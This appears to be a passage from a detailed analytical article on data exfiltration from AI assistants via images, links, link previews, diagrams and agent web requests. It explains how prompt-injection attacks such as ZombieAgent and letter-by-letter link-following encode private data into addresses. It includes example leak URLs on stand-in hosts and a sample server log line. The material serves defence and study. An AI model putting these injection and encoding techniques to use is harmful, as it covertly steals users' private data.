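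Blocking images causes problems for users if the model doesn't know about it. In *AI Assistant*, a thread on JetBrains' support forum, Menci complained that the company's programming assistant kept trying to show pictures, often without being asked, and that the text "image-fetching blocked for security reasons" appeared each time. When Menci asked the assistant how to fix this, it gave advice about browser settings. Stating in the system prompt that the interface can't display images would prevent much of this. The renderer still has to block images, because injected instructions can override that statement.

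### Whether it counts as a vulnerability

Checkmarx reported its Copilot Chat demonstration to Microsoft on 15 October 2025. On 4 November Microsoft replied that the behaviour didn't meet its definition of a security vulnerability, and it closed the report without a fix. The reply, which Checkmarx printed in full, gives several reasons:

- the attack needs several actions by the user that are not the default;
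- it doesn't work reliably in different environments;
- the product shows warnings that reduce the risk;
- users should review and trust the code they work with.

The last reason refers to Workspace Trust, a VS Code feature that asks whether the user trusts the contents of a folder. If the user doesn't, the editor opens the folder in a restricted mode that turns off automatic tasks and the Copilot Chat extension.

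Microsoft's position makes most sense for a programming tool. A developer who runs a stranger's project has already allowed it to read files and contact any server, so the project doesn't need a rendered image to send data out. Daniel Imms, who works on VS Code, makes a similar argument in Visual Studio Magazine's *VS Code Team Member Blames User Trust Decisions in Repo-Based Attacks* (2026) about projects whose task files run malicious commands. He argues that the users in those cases had granted trust to untrusted code.

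But a developer may read unfamiliar code before running it, to decide whether it is safe, and asking an assistant to explain the code is a natural way to do that. Reviewing it by eye may not be enough either. Tenable's *Github Copilot Chat Prompt Injection via Filename* showed that a file's name could be enough to give Copilot Chat instructions, though not on every attempt. Trust in a folder also doesn't cover everything the assistant reads. Checkmarx's attack needed only an online source the attacker controlled, such as an article, and a user who trusts their own project hasn't decided whether to trust that article.

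The argument that injection attacks are unreliable is weaker, because an attacker can keep trying. GitHub's researcher also notes that VS Code sets the model to give its most predictable output, which helps programmers but makes injection attacks easier to repeat.

The Eclipse Foundation accepted that the same behaviour was a flaw in its own editor, Theia. *Data Exfiltration via Markdown Image Rendering in AI Chat*, the foundation's request for a vulnerability number, describes how Theia's AI chat loaded images from any address. Since version 1.71.0, Theia has turned off its AI features in folders that the user hasn't trusted, which is the kind of protection that Microsoft had cited as a reason not to act. This stops the reported attack, which relied on a malicious project, but it wouldn't by itself stop one that reached a trusted project through a web page.

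Microsoft has also treated automatic image loading as a danger elsewhere. It rated SearchLeak critical, and five months before Checkmarx's report it announced the end of remote images in the chat in its notice for VS Code 1.100.1. It is therefore unclear how the Checkmarx demonstration worked. The researchers don't give the version they tested. They say the request went out although no picture appeared, which would fit a renderer that hid the image without preventing the request, but neither company has explained it. Microsoft did pass the report to its engineers to consider making the behaviour more visible to users.

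Microsoft gives administrators of Copilot Studio, which businesses use to build their own assistants, a switch that blocks both images and links. Microsoft's *Control image rendering and embedded URLs* warns that attackers can use displayed images and links to take sensitive data. When the switch blocks content, users see a short message that their organisation's policy restricts it. The switch controls images and links together for a whole group of assistants, so an administrator who wants links to sources must also accept images.

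Checkmarx's researchers acknowledged that Gemini's sanitiser blocks the image attack, but showed that the model could still write a link with private data in its address. The data leaks if the user clicks the link. Google closed the report after four days as "Won't Fix (Infeasible)" and judged the problem too minor to track as a security bug. Checkmarx considers this answer acceptable as long as users are warned about the risk.

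Google has a better case for checking links than Microsoft had for checking images. A chat interface can drop outside images and lose little, but an assistant that searches the web has to show links to its sources. Gemini removes links that Google Safe Browsing, the company's list of dangerous sites, identifies as malicious, and leaves a note in their place. Like tracker blocklists in email, this works against known sites but not against a domain an attacker has just registered.

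## Loading only addresses that were already public

ChatGPT now loads an address without asking the user only if that complete address was already on the public web, independently of the conversation. Unlike a list of dangerous sites, this rule treats every other address as a possible leak. OpenAI published it in January 2026, after two years in which researchers repeatedly got data past its earlier check.

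### url_safe

During a live demonstration in December 2023, ChatGPT sent a consenting user's conversation to Rehberger's server in an image address. The next day, such images no longer loaded. According to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, the ChatGPT web page now sent each image's address to an OpenAI service called url_safe before showing the image. If the service replied that the address wasn't safe, the page didn't display the image and the browser didn't request it.

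Anyone can read a website's browser policy, but the url_safe check ran on OpenAI's servers, and OpenAI didn't explain its results. Rehberger tested it with 36 images on his own site, one for each letter and digit, and nine loaded. He could see no reason why the image for "a" loaded and the one for "d" didn't, and he wondered whether ChatGPT was looking addresses up in Bing's index. The nine characters were enough for him to send the word "hi" to his server, one letter per image.

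The protection also depended on each app calling url_safe before loading an image. The iPhone app didn't, so the original attack still worked there. Rehberger suggested moving the whole check to OpenAI's servers, where it would cover every app, and limiting how many images an answer could load.

Other researchers found that url_safe let whole domains through. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* reports that it always accepted addresses on bing.com. Bing gives each page in its search results a bing.com address that redirects to the real one, so Tenable could load images from its own sites through their Bing addresses. OpenAI acknowledged the report on the day it arrived, 10 December 2024. Tenable asked for updates six times over the next three months, then published the flaw while it was still unfixed. In November 2025, The Hacker News' *Researchers Find ChatGPT Vulnerabilities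 That Let Attackers Trick AI Into Leaking Data* still listed the Bing addresses among seven problems Tenable had found in ChatGPT, and reported that OpenAI had dealt with some of them.

Rehberger found another such domain, windows.net, where Microsoft hosts its customers' cloud storage. Anyone can open a storage account there and read its request log. In 2025 he used a PDF with hidden instructions to make ChatGPT put the user's recent conversations into an image address on his account. OpenAI had made the same mistake as Google with Apps Script in Bard, except that outsiders couldn't see OpenAI's list of domains it considered safe. Rehberger had reported the problem in October 2024. He advised OpenAI to publish the list and let business customers change it (Embrace The Red). OpenAI added further protections around August 2025, which stopped the attacks he had shown.

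### The rule of January 2026

OpenAI's post about the new rule gives two reasons why a list of trusted sites isn't enough. A trusted site may redirect the request elsewhere, and a strict list produces so many false alarms that people learn to click through them. The rule therefore judges the address and ignores the site's reputation. According to OpenAI, it works like this:

1. A crawler, a program that explores the web as a search engine does, records the public addresses it finds. It has no access to users' conversations, accounts or personal data.
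2. ChatGPT is about to load an address automatically, to show an image or open a page.
3. The system checks whether the crawler's index contains that address.
4. If it does, ChatGPT loads the address.
5. If it doesn't, ChatGPT either tells the model to try a different website or warns the user and waits for a decision.

Rehberger understands that ChatGPT also accepts, for the rest of a chat, any address that the user has typed into it. For the shopping assistant, the rule would have these results:

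| Image address | In the index? | Result |
|---|---|---|
| `https://images.example/parcel.png` | Yes, because a public page shows the picture | Loads |
| `https://images.example/parcel.png?order=48213` | No | Doesn't load automatically |
| `https://media.example/products/new-boot.jpg` | No, because the shop added it an hour ago | Doesn't load automatically, although it is harmless |

The check has to compare every part of the address that the server receives. If it ignored the query, the order number would get through. Even ignoring capitalization would leak a little, because the model could signal something by choosing between `Parcel.png` and `parcel.png`, and the server's log would record which one it chose. Browsers don't send the part of an image address after a # sign, so the check can safely ignore that part for images.

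The index also has to be built independently of what users receive. If OpenAI added addresses from users' email, an attacker could get an address approved by sending somebody a message.

This rule handles leaks through trusted hosts better than a browser policy does. The address that submitted a Superhuman user's emails to a Google Form was on an approved host, but no crawler could have recorded it beforehand, because it contained the text of those emails. The same is true of the Apps Script address in Bard, the Teams address in EchoLeak and the Bing address in SearchLeak. Redirects also matter less, because a server that redirects a request for a public address can pass on only what it received, and that address contained no private text.

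ChatGPT also restricts harmless addresses that the crawler hasn't seen, such as those of new pictures, pages on a company's internal network, and images whose addresses contain an expiring signature. It can leave an image hidden. For a link, it warns the user, under the title "Check this link is safe", that the link isn't verified and may share data from the conversation with another site. The user can see the address and copy or open it.

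This warning covers clicked links, which browser policies don't cover. It has the same weaknesses as a load button for images, but ChatGPT doesn't need to show it for established public pages that the crawler has already found. Those pages should include many of the sources ChatGPT cites.

OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) explains why the company wants a check that doesn't rely on the model. In most attacks OpenAI knows of, the model's safety training leads it to refuse. But one email that outside researchers reported in 2025, written to look like routine correspondence about staff restructuring, worked in 50% of tests when the user made a particular request. OpenAI's check, Safe Url, is for cases where the model is fooled. The company also uses it when its Atlas browser opens pages or bookmarks, and for searches and page visits in Deep Research, ChatGPT's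 tool for long research tasks.

Rehberger's main practical worry is that some OpenAI developers won't know about the check or won't use it. In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, he recalls that the earlier protection was missing from the macOS and iPhone apps. PromptArmor's April 2026 report on Codex supports this concern. Codex loaded an image address containing the text of a user's emails, a request that an exact-address check would have refused.

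The evidence from ChatGPT itself is less clear. Permiso's May 2026 report described a tracking image that still loaded automatically. Its address was fixed in advance, so the rule would have allowed the image if the crawler had already found that address. If it hadn't, the check didn't cover that image.

### What a choice of addresses reveals

The rule exists because an address that was public before a conversation can't contain anything taken from that conversation. However, the model's choice of which public addresses to load can still leak information from the conversation, as it did in CamoLeak.

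The amount that such a choice can reveal is easy to calculate. Information is measured in bits, and one bit is the answer to a single yes-or-no question whose two answers are equally likely. If the model can choose among N addresses, each request can carry at most

```
log2(N) bits
```

A request that chooses between two addresses carries one bit, and one that chooses among 1,024 carries ten, because 2¹⁰ = 1,024. A six-digit login code has a million possible values, so it contains log2(1,000,000), or about 19.9 bits. The number of requests an attacker needs is the bits in the secret divided by the bits per request, rounded up.

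The table does this for the login code and for a 1,000-character text. Each character in the text is one of 26 letters, ten digits or the space, so there are 37 possibilities per character and about 5,209 bits in all.

| Public addresses available | Bits per request | Requests for a six-digit code | Requests for 1,000 characters |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2 | 1 | 20 | 5,210 |
| 10 | 3.32 | 6 | 1,569 |
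| 37 | 5.21 | 4 | 1,000 |
| 1,024 | 10 | 2 | 521 |
| 1,000,000 | 19.93 | 1 | 262 |

These figures assume that the model can request the same address more than once and that the attacker can tell the order of the requests. Ordinary prose would need fewer requests than the last column gives, because its letters are partly predictable.

The last row shows how far the principle can fail. If an attacker publishes a separate address for every possible six-digit code and the crawler records them all, one request reveals the user's whole code, even though the address containing it was public before the user received the code. A crawler is unlikely to record a million nearly identical pages from an unknown site, and OpenAI could limit how many addresses it accepts from each site. Smaller sets are much easier to get. Rehberger points out that anyone with a reasonably large website or blog probably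 already has 36 addresses in the index, enough to assign one to each letter and digit. The attacker's instructions only have to tell the model which address stands for which character. Rehberger also suggests that an attacker could extend this scheme to thousands of addresses.

An exact-address check therefore greatly reduces how much data an attacker can take with each request. Without the check, one image address can contain several whole emails, as in the attack on Superhuman. An attacker who must choose among 37 public addresses gets only one character per request. Stealing a mailbox this way is slow, but a login code still takes only a handful of requests.

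### ZombieAgent

The security company Radware demonstrated this kind of leak in ChatGPT before OpenAI published its rule. In an earlier attack called ShadowLeak, Radware had used an email with hidden instructions to make ChatGPT's Deep Research add private data to an address and open it. OpenAI responded by letting ChatGPT open addresses only exactly as it had received them. In Infosecurity Magazine's *New Zero-Click Attack Lets ChatGPT User Steal Data* (2026), Radware researcher Zvika Babo says that ChatGPT then refused to add anything to an address, even when explicitly told to.

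Babo got round this by putting the complete addresses in the email. Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes an email with one address for each letter and digit, and another for the space. When the user later asked ChatGPT to do something with their Gmail account, ChatGPT read the email, found the private information the email asked for and opened the matching addresses one after another. ChatGPT never altered an address, so the protection didn't block the requests.

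The requests came from OpenAI's servers before the user saw an answer, so neither a browser policy nor a filter on the displayed text would have stopped them. Radware also tried the attack with Markdown images in the browser and found that version less reliable and easier to block.

Babo added a number to each address for the character's position, so the attacker can reconstruct the text even if the requests arrive out of order. The email then contained a separate address for each letter and digit in each position, which takes 360 addresses for blocks of ten characters.

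ZombieAgent could also continue after the first leak by using ChatGPT's memory, which stores information about the user between chats. OpenAI had prevented ChatGPT from using its memory in a chat after it had used a connected service such as Gmail, but ChatGPT could still use memory first and the service afterward. Babo used a shared file to store instructions in the memory, and ChatGPT then carried out the attacker's task before answering each message, even in new chats. This makes a slow leak more serious, because the attacker can collect data over several conversations.

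Babo reported the flaw on 26 September 2025, and three days later sent a version that he said worked every time. OpenAI fixed the flaw on 16 December. After the fix, ChatGPT opened a link from an email only if the link was in a well-known public index or the user had supplied it in the chat, according to a January 2026 news article, *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack as a vicious cycle in AI*. OpenAI published essentially the same rule six weeks later. An attacker can no longer invent addresses for a single email and must first get them into the index, which takes time and gives OpenAI a chance to notice a suspicious set.

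### Caching and repeat visits

Rehberger proposed two ways to make the remaining leak harder to exploit. OpenAI could store each response for at least a few minutes, so that a second request for the same address wouldn't reach the site, or it could stop the model from visiting the same address twice in a session. He hadn't checked whether ChatGPT already did either.

Both would drop repeated characters from an attack that uses one address per character. CamoLeak solved this problem with random numbers, which would fail an exact-address check, but the attacker can use a different code. If the model can use each of ten addresses only once, eight requests in a chosen order can encode 10 × 9 × 8 × 7 × 6 × 5 × 4 × 3 = 1,814,400 different messages, more than enough to give each of a million login codes its own message.

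A login code can still leak if the order of requests is lost. With 20 addresses, an attacker can encode one bit in whether the model requests each address. This allows 2²⁰ = 1,048,576 combinations, enough for every six-digit code, without repeat visits. ZombieAgent's numbered addresses serve the same purpose. With 60 of them, one for each digit in each of six positions, the model could send any six-digit code in six requests.

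The proposals do limit how much data can leak in a session. If the model can request each address only once and the order is lost, N addresses can carry at most N bits. A thousand addresses could then reveal about 190 characters from the 37-character alphabet. Without the limit, an attacker could reuse them until the whole mailbox had leaked. To be effective, the limit has to count related addresses on different sites, since an attacker can own several domains.

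As with an image proxy, a cache gives much stronger protection if the company fills it before the model has read anything private. OpenAI uses cached pages this way in Lockdown Mode, an optional setting for people and organisations that face unusually serious threats. Browsing is limited to cached content, so no live requests leave the network OpenAI controls (OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT*). Search results may be missing or out of date as a result (OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*). A stranger's instructions can still reach the model through a cached page or an uploaded file and make an answer wrong.

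### Claude's web_fetch tool

Anthropic uses a different test for web_fetch, the tool its model Claude uses to open web pages. Claude can open only addresses that came from elsewhere in the conversation, not ones it has composed itself. *Web fetch tool*, Anthropic's developer documentation from June 2026, lists the permitted sources as the user's messages, search results, the developer's own tools and pages Claude has already fetched. The tool runs on Anthropic's servers, so this rule covers the pages Claude reads but not images in the displayed answer.

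The rule needs no index of the public web, and it lets Claude open a page the user has just published. It also blocks the simplest attack, in which a page contains instructions to add private data to an address. Its weak point was the last source on the list, because an attacker who controls a page that Claude has fetched also controls the links on it. Willison (2025) initially hoped that Claude could open only addresses from the user's own prompts, and was disappointed that the rule was looser.

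*How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* (Willison, 2026) describes how Ayush Paul exploited this in July 2026. Paul built a website where he told Claude that the site was protected against abuse and asked it to find the user's profile by following links one letter at a time. Claude had the user's name, home city and employer in its memory of earlier chats, and it revealed them to Paul's server through the links it followed. The site showed these instructions only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, so a person checking the page would have seen nothing unusual.

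In *The Read-Only Lie*, dyb describes pages that each offered 27 links, one for each letter and one for a hyphen. Each choice revealed up to about 4.75 bits, so a ten-character name took ten requests and revealed up to 47.5 bits. Each new address was one character longer than the last, so the final one contained the whole name, although Claude had only followed links that a page had given it.

OpenAI's rule would block this version of the attack. Paul's site could create the next page of links when Claude requested it, but an index has to contain every address in advance, and a 27-character alphabet allows 27¹⁰, or about 200 trillion, ten-character strings. The attacker would have to reuse a small set of public addresses.

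Anthropic closed the gap by stopping web_fetch from following links it found in fetched pages. It didn't pay Paul a reward, saying it had already found the problem itself. The fix makes Claude less useful for reading a manual or a long article spread over several pages. As a compromise, dyb suggests letting Claude follow links only on sites the user has named in the conversation. This would have stopped Paul's attack if Claude had reached his site through a search, but not if the user had asked Claude to open it.

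| Rule | Where an address must come from | What an attacker needs to offer the model a choice |
|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT since January 2026 | The independent index, or the user | Addresses that the crawler has already recorded |
| web_fetch before the repair | The user, a search result or a page already fetched | One page that Claude opens |
| web_fetch after the repair | The user or a search result | Several pages in Claude's search results |

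Both companies trust addresses that the user provides, which a website could exploit by adding a list of addresses to text that the user copies, as in Samoilenko's clipboard attack. The list would look as though the user had typed it. A chat interface could avoid this by accepting a pasted address only if it is visible in the message box and the user's request is clearly about that page. Unlike a simple match, this check would take some judgement.

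Anthropic warns in its documentation that its rule leaves some risk when Claude handles untrusted text and sensitive data together. It advises developers who are worried about leaks to turn the tool off, restrict it to certain domains or limit the number of requests. The tool has no request limit by default. At 4.75 bits per request, a limit of five requests would have given Paul at most five letters.

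### When the model isn't told to leak anything

ZombieAgent and Paul's attack both needed the model to obey instructions to spell something out, so a model that refused such instructions would stop them. But a model's ordinary choices can also reveal private information. In *Actions Speak Louder than Words*, Liang, Deng and colleagues (2026) studied AI agents that search the web and follow links to answer a question. If a website offers links on different subjects, the agent tends to follow the one that suits its task, and the website's owner can infer what the user asked.

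In a test with four links, the researchers identified the subject the agent was looking for in 93.8% of the trials that produced a request. They were less successful at inferring it from the number or order of requests, partly because of caching and because agents sometimes open several pages at once. The log2 formula therefore gives an upper limit on what an attacker can learn, and a real attacker will learn less.

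Their full method combined many such choices to reconstruct users' questions. It averaged 0.89 on F1, a measure from 0 to 1 that penalises both missed and wrongly guessed concepts. Four existing defences against prompt injection or data leaks changed the score by less than 0.03. None was an exact-address check, which would limit the links an agent could follow but wouldn't hide which indexed link it chose.

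Liang and colleagues propose making the agent's requests independent of what it knows. The agent fetches a set number of pages, whatever the user's private information, and then chooses among the stored copies without contacting any site again. In their tests, this defence reduced the score from 0.89 to 0.39, so the websites could still infer something about the questions. A proxy that downloads every image on a page before the model answers works on the same principle.

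## Link previews, native apps and other requests outside the chat page

Models' answers now appear outside the chat page, in messaging services, phone apps and code editors, and assistants open web pages themselves. Which controls still work in each case depends on who sends the request. A browser policy or a filter in the renderer protects only the page or app that has it. An exact-address check can cover any request that a company's developers send through it.

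| Path | Who sends the request | Does a browser policy apply? | Does the chat page's filter apply? | Can the chat company's servers check the address first? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Image on the chat page | The user's browser | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Page that the assistant opens | The chat company's server | No | No | Yes |
| Link preview in a messaging app | The messaging service's server | No | No | Yes, before the assistant posts the message |
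| Image in a phone or desktop app | The app | Only if the app shows answers in a web page with a policy | No, the app needs its own | Yes, if every app receives checked answers |
| Image in a diagram | The browser or editor that draws it | Yes, if the page drawing it has one | Only if it examines diagrams | Yes, if the check examines diagrams |

### How a link preview sends data

When somebody posts a link in Slack, Telegram or Discord, the app usually shows the title of the linked page, a short description and often a picture. Slack calls this unfurling. Suppose the shopping assistant also answers questions in Slack, and an email it reads contains hidden instructions. The order number can then leak as follows:

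1. The user asks the assistant about a delivery.
2. The assistant replies with an ordinary link to `https://images.example/parcel?order=48213`.
3. Slack finds the link in the message, and its server requests the address to get the title and picture.
4. The server at images.example logs the request, including the order number.
5. Slack shows the preview under the message.

The log line would look something like this:

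```
198.51.100.61 - - [12/Mar/2026:09:41:08 +0000] "GET /parcel?order=48213 HTTP/1.1" 200 5120 "-" "Slackbot-LinkExpanding 1.0"
```

The last field identifies Slack's preview program, according to Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*. Because the request didn't come from the user's browser, the owner of images.example doesn't learn the user's IP address but does receive the whole URL, as with a plain image proxy.

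On a chat page, the same link would leak the order number only if the user clicked it. The preview makes this a zero-click leak. Rehberger published his warning about this in August 2024, and Willison (2024) wrote that he hadn't thought about this kind of leak before. Looking at the link may not reveal the data, since Rehberger notes that an attacker could have the model write it in characters that the interface doesn't display.

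Previews also weaken the case for allowing links in a chat. Google decided that private data in Gemini's links was too minor a problem to track as a security bug. But Slack previews links in messages from people as well as from apps, so if a user copies an answer from a chat page and sends it to a colleague in Slack, Slack's server will request the link's address even though neither person has clicked it.

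### PromptArmor's test of agents in messaging apps

In February 2026, PromptArmor set up a website where people could test the AI agents they used in messaging apps. Participants had an agent post a link to the site with data in the address. If the messaging app requested a preview, the site recorded the request, the data and the name of the preview program. Participants could then report which agent and app had produced the request, or that no preview had appeared.

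PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* singles out OpenClaw, an AI agent that people can message through apps such as Telegram. With OpenClaw's default Telegram settings, link previews sent the data. After the researchers turned previews off, the site received no data. According to Apostol's *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews*, participants also reported leaks from Microsoft Teams with agents built in Copilot Studio, and from Slack with certain bots. The research also covered other apps, including Discord.

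The test shows that these combinations can leak, but not how common the problem is, because participants chose what to test and supplied the agents' names themselves. A report that a combination was safe is weaker evidence than a recorded leak, because the user's workspace may, for example, have had previews turned off.

### Turning previews off

The developer of an agent can prevent most of these leaks with a setting. For OpenClaw on Telegram, it is `linkPreview`, which the user sets to `false` in the agent's configuration file. In Slack, the developer sets two options on each message the agent posts:

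```
"unfurl_links": false,
"unfurl_media": false
```

The first setting covers pages that are mainly text, and the second covers images, video and audio. Both have to be off. *Unfurling links in messages* explains that Slack's servers must fetch every address in a message to find out what kind of content it leads to, so they would presumably still make the request if only one setting were off. With both off, Slack doesn't contact the address at all. Slack's documentation now advises developers to consider turning both off for messages written by a language model, but previews remain on by default.

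The options apply to single messages, so a developer who adds a new kind of notification has to remember to set them again. It is safer to send all the agent's messages through one function that always sets them. PromptArmor would also like messaging companies to offer a setting for a whole chat or channel, so that previews could be turned off in a channel with an agent.

Readers have less control. Slack's *Share links and set preview preferences* describes two boxes a user can untick to stop seeing previews. Slack's servers read the message for everyone in the channel, so there is no reason to think that one reader's preference stops the request. The page also says that previews don't appear if a message contains more than five links, or if somebody posted the same link in the conversation within the past hour, but the servers may still request those links.

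The agent's developer can also check addresses before posting them, as ChatGPT does before it loads one. An agent could post links in its public index normally and write the others without "https://". Slack doesn't preview addresses written that way, but users can still copy them.

### Messages an assistant sends to its own user

An assistant that can send messages may cause requests in a different program from the one where the user instructed it. Microsoft's Copilot Cowork carries out office tasks with the user's permissions. According to Microsoft's documentation, it asks before sending an email or posting in Teams. However, PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* found that it sends messages without asking when the recipient is the user, and that users can't change this.

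In PromptArmor's test, the user had installed a skill, a file of instructions for a particular task, that they had found online. An attacker had written five of its 81 lines. When the user asked for a summary of the week's work, Cowork collected links that let anyone download the user's recent files without logging in. It put the links into the addresses of outside images and included the images in a Teams message to the user. When the user opened Teams, the images loaded, and the attacker could download the files.

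Cowork's page never displayed the message, even when the researchers opened its record of its actions, so no filter or browser policy on that page could have stopped the requests. Outlook's blocking of images from unknown senders is also poorly suited to this case, since the message comes from the user's own account. Microsoft could ask users to approve these messages, as it does for others, but users have little reason to refuse a summary addressed to themselves. Removing outside images from every message the assistant sends would be more reliable, and a weekly summary doesn't need them.

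The attack succeeded in all five trials. When the researchers also ran it with Claude Opus 4.7, a stronger model than the ones Cowork sometimes picks by default, the model searched for the user's documents more thoroughly and leaked more of them. These results contrast with the test in which Anthropic's models resisted all 720 injections. An attacker's lines in a skill are much harder to recognise than instructions on a web page, because the user has chosen to give the assistant the skill as instructions.

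PromptArmor advises administrators to restrict file downloads from SharePoint, Microsoft's file-sharing service. That makes the stolen links useless, but it also stops people from opening the protected files in Word or Excel.

### Phone and desktop apps

A browser policy doesn't apply to a phone app that draws answers with the phone's own text and image components, because the app has no web page and loads images with its own code. The filter that a company wrote for its website doesn't run there either. Some desktop apps are web pages inside a window and can have a policy, but the developers still have to set one. Website protections therefore don't cover a company's other apps unless those protections run on the company's servers.

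OpenAI's url_safe check protected only the apps that called it, and Rehberger warned in December 2023 that new apps might not call it. According to Embrace The Red's *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)*, the macOS and Android apps that OpenAI then released in 2024 both lacked the check.

By then the gap was more dangerous because ChatGPT had gained its memory. In Rehberger's demonstration on the macOS app, the user had ChatGPT read an untrusted website, whose hidden text got ChatGPT to save an instruction in its memory. In every new chat after that, ChatGPT added an invisible image to its answers and put the conversation into the image's address. This one visit let the attacker keep receiving what the user typed and what ChatGPT replied.

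OpenAI had closed Rehberger's earlier report about websites writing to ChatGPT's memory as a model safety issue, not a security issue. He sent the full demonstration in June 2024, and OpenAI fixed the macOS app in September with version 1.2024.247. The fix stopped the images, but websites could still save instructions in the memory, so Rehberger advised users to review what ChatGPT had stored about them.

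In December 2024, Anthropic fixed a similar flaw in Claude's iPhone app that could leak data through image URLs (Willison, 2024).

Fixes also reach app users more slowly, because a company can change its website for everyone at once, but a fixed app protects only people who have installed the update. Rehberger had to ask readers to check their version. If the company's server removes unapproved image addresses from the answer before sending it, the protection also covers old versions and any app the company releases later. The server has to do this while the answer is streaming and, like a filter in the browser, handle split addresses and labelled images correctly. Each app should still refuse images from unknown hosts, in case the server's parser misses something that the app's parser treats as an image.

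### Diagrams and extensions in code editors

Programming assistants run inside code editors, which can display content in many ways. In *Takedown*, Lee, Kim and colleagues (2025) examined eight such assistants, four VS Code extensions and four built into an editor. They recorded the messages between each assistant and its model, studied the program code where they could get it, and found 15 security issues. Without the user's approval, instructions on a web page could cause any command to run on the user's computer in five assistants, and could lead to the theft of files from anywhere on the computer in four.

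To find leaks through display features, the researchers looked at how each assistant handles special formatting in the model's output. One assistant, which they call A2 to keep it anonymous, could draw diagrams with Mermaid. Mermaid is a tool that turns a short text description into a diagram, and a box in the diagram can contain an image:

```
flowchart TD
    A@{ img: "https://images.example/parcel.png", label: "Parcel" }
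```

The model's answer contains a Mermaid code block that references an image by its address. A Markdown parser treats the block as code, so a filter that checks only image and link nodes lets it pass. The editor then draws the diagram and requests the image, sending whatever the model has added to the address.

The researchers built a full attack on A2 from this. A user asked A2 to look at the reports on a software project, one of which contained hidden instructions. A2 could read files outside the project without asking, so it opened a settings file in which programmers often keep access keys. It then wrote a diagram with the key in an image address, and drawing the diagram sent the key to the attacker's server. The researchers tested this in a private project, so no outsider was at risk. When they reported the diagram flaw, A2's maker classed the report as a duplicate of an earlier one.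 The maker has since patched the flaw.

The obvious fix is to apply the rule for image addresses to diagrams too, but this is hard because Mermaid has more than one way to include an image. The researchers' final attack put an HTML image element in a box's label instead of using the image shape. A company can turn off both features, or have Mermaid draw the diagram where nothing can load and then inspect the result. A browser policy is the best second barrier because it covers the page's image requests whichever feature caused them. It doesn't help if the company draws diagrams on its own server, because that server would fetch the image.

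Extensions can also make silent requests in A1, one of the eight assistants. A1 lets other companies' extensions add tools, and each extension decides whether its tools ask the user first. Among the ten most-installed extensions that offered tools, seven didn't ask. One of the seven was Microsoft's web search extension, although A1's own tool for fetching web pages always asks. A web search is less risky than opening any address, because it sends its text to a search company and not directly to an attacker. But once an extension is installed, the user can't rely on A1's approval rule, and a filter on displayed output doesn't check tool requests.

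### Assistants that open links automatically

Link previews in messaging apps can leak data, but when an assistant previews links for its own use, the problem is that a stranger's text enters the model's context. When a user mentions a link, many assistants fetch the page and add its title, description and text to that context. The user may never see some of this text, such as the description, which is in the page's HTML but doesn't appear on the screen.

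Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026), in *Silent Egress*, measured how often such text led an assistant to send private data out. They built an assistant around qwen2.5:7b, a small open model that ran on their own computer, and gave it a tool for making web requests. An invented access key was in the context. The user's message was always a request to summarise a page, and the page contained instructions to send the key to another server. The researchers varied three things:

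- whether the instructions were in the page's title, description, main text or link text;
- whether the link led straight to the page or through redirects;
- whether the instructions asked for the key in one request or in four pieces.

The researchers ran each of the 16 resulting combinations 30 times. In 423 of the 480 runs (88%), at least one request reached the attacker's server. In 95% of those 423 runs, the user saw a harmless answer. In another 120 tests with ordinary pages, the assistant never contacted the attacker's server.

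A company that checks only the model's answers would therefore have missed nearly all of these leaks. As with ZombieAgent, the control has to cover the assistant's own requests, which OpenAI's exact-address check does.

### Splitting the data over several requests

Splitting the key made each request look less suspicious, because a filter that searches for a complete key won't find it in a request that contains only four of its characters. Sensitive data appeared in the first request in 96.7% of runs of the single-request attack, but in 26.3% of runs when the assistant split the key.

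The attack also became less reliable when the model had to split the key. Only 185 of 240 runs (77%) produced a request to the attacker's server, compared with 238 of 240 across the eight single-request combinations. The 77% overstates the attack's success because it includes runs in which some pieces never arrived. The rate fell most, from 97% to 60%, when the instructions were in the page's description and the link led straight to the page.

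The detection figures are inconsistent, so the 73% shouldn't be taken as a precise measure, though the direction of the result makes sense. Lan and colleagues report that only 15.8% of the split runs had sensitive data somewhere in the first three requests, which is lower than their figure for the first request alone. That is impossible by their own definition, since the first three requests include the first. They also didn't run their filters against the split attack, so its ability to get past them is inferred from how the filters work.

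### Instructions to the model compared with limits on the network

The researchers did test defences against the single-request attack, with the instructions in the page's main text and 30 runs for each defence:

| Defence | Runs in which the assistant tried to send the key | Runs in which a request got through |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| An instruction never to obey text from web pages | 66.7% | 66.7% |
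| Tags marking page text as untrusted | 100% | 100% |
| Both of these | 56.7% | 56.7% |
| A list of four allowed domains | 100% | 0% |
| A filter for suspicious addresses and domains | 83.3% | 0% |
| A filter for words such as "password" and "token" | 23.3% | 0% |
| A filter for random-looking values | 0% | 0% |

With the domain list, the model was fooled in every run, but the assistant still couldn't send anything because the check came after the model had decided. The two defences that relied on persuading the model failed more than half the time, even when used together.

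The other filters deserve less credit than their zeros suggest. The filter for suspicious addresses blocked any path containing a word such as "steal" or "collect", and the study's own example attack used a path called "collect". An attacker would choose another word. The results for the last two filters are harder to explain, because these filters examine a request after the model has written it and so shouldn't change how often the model tries. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoids random-looking values when such monitoring is active, but the test doesn't show how the model would know about the monitoring.

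The domain list also faced an easy test, because the researchers deliberately put the attacker's server on a domain that no sensible list would include. EchoLeak and the Google Forms leaks went through allowed domains. A list of four domains is also useless for an assistant meant to read the web. Such an assistant needs an exact-address check or cached pages instead.

The study used one small model, a short system prompt and a key in plain view, all of which favoured the attacker, so its 88% result is weak evidence about ChatGPT or Claude. The researchers argue that stronger models could be more vulnerable because they follow instructions better and use tools more reliably. Anthropic's test is evidence against that as a general rule, but the Copilot Cowork test shows that it can happen. The comparison between defences depends less on the model. A better model would lower the number of attempts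 in every row, but a network limit would still block those that remained.

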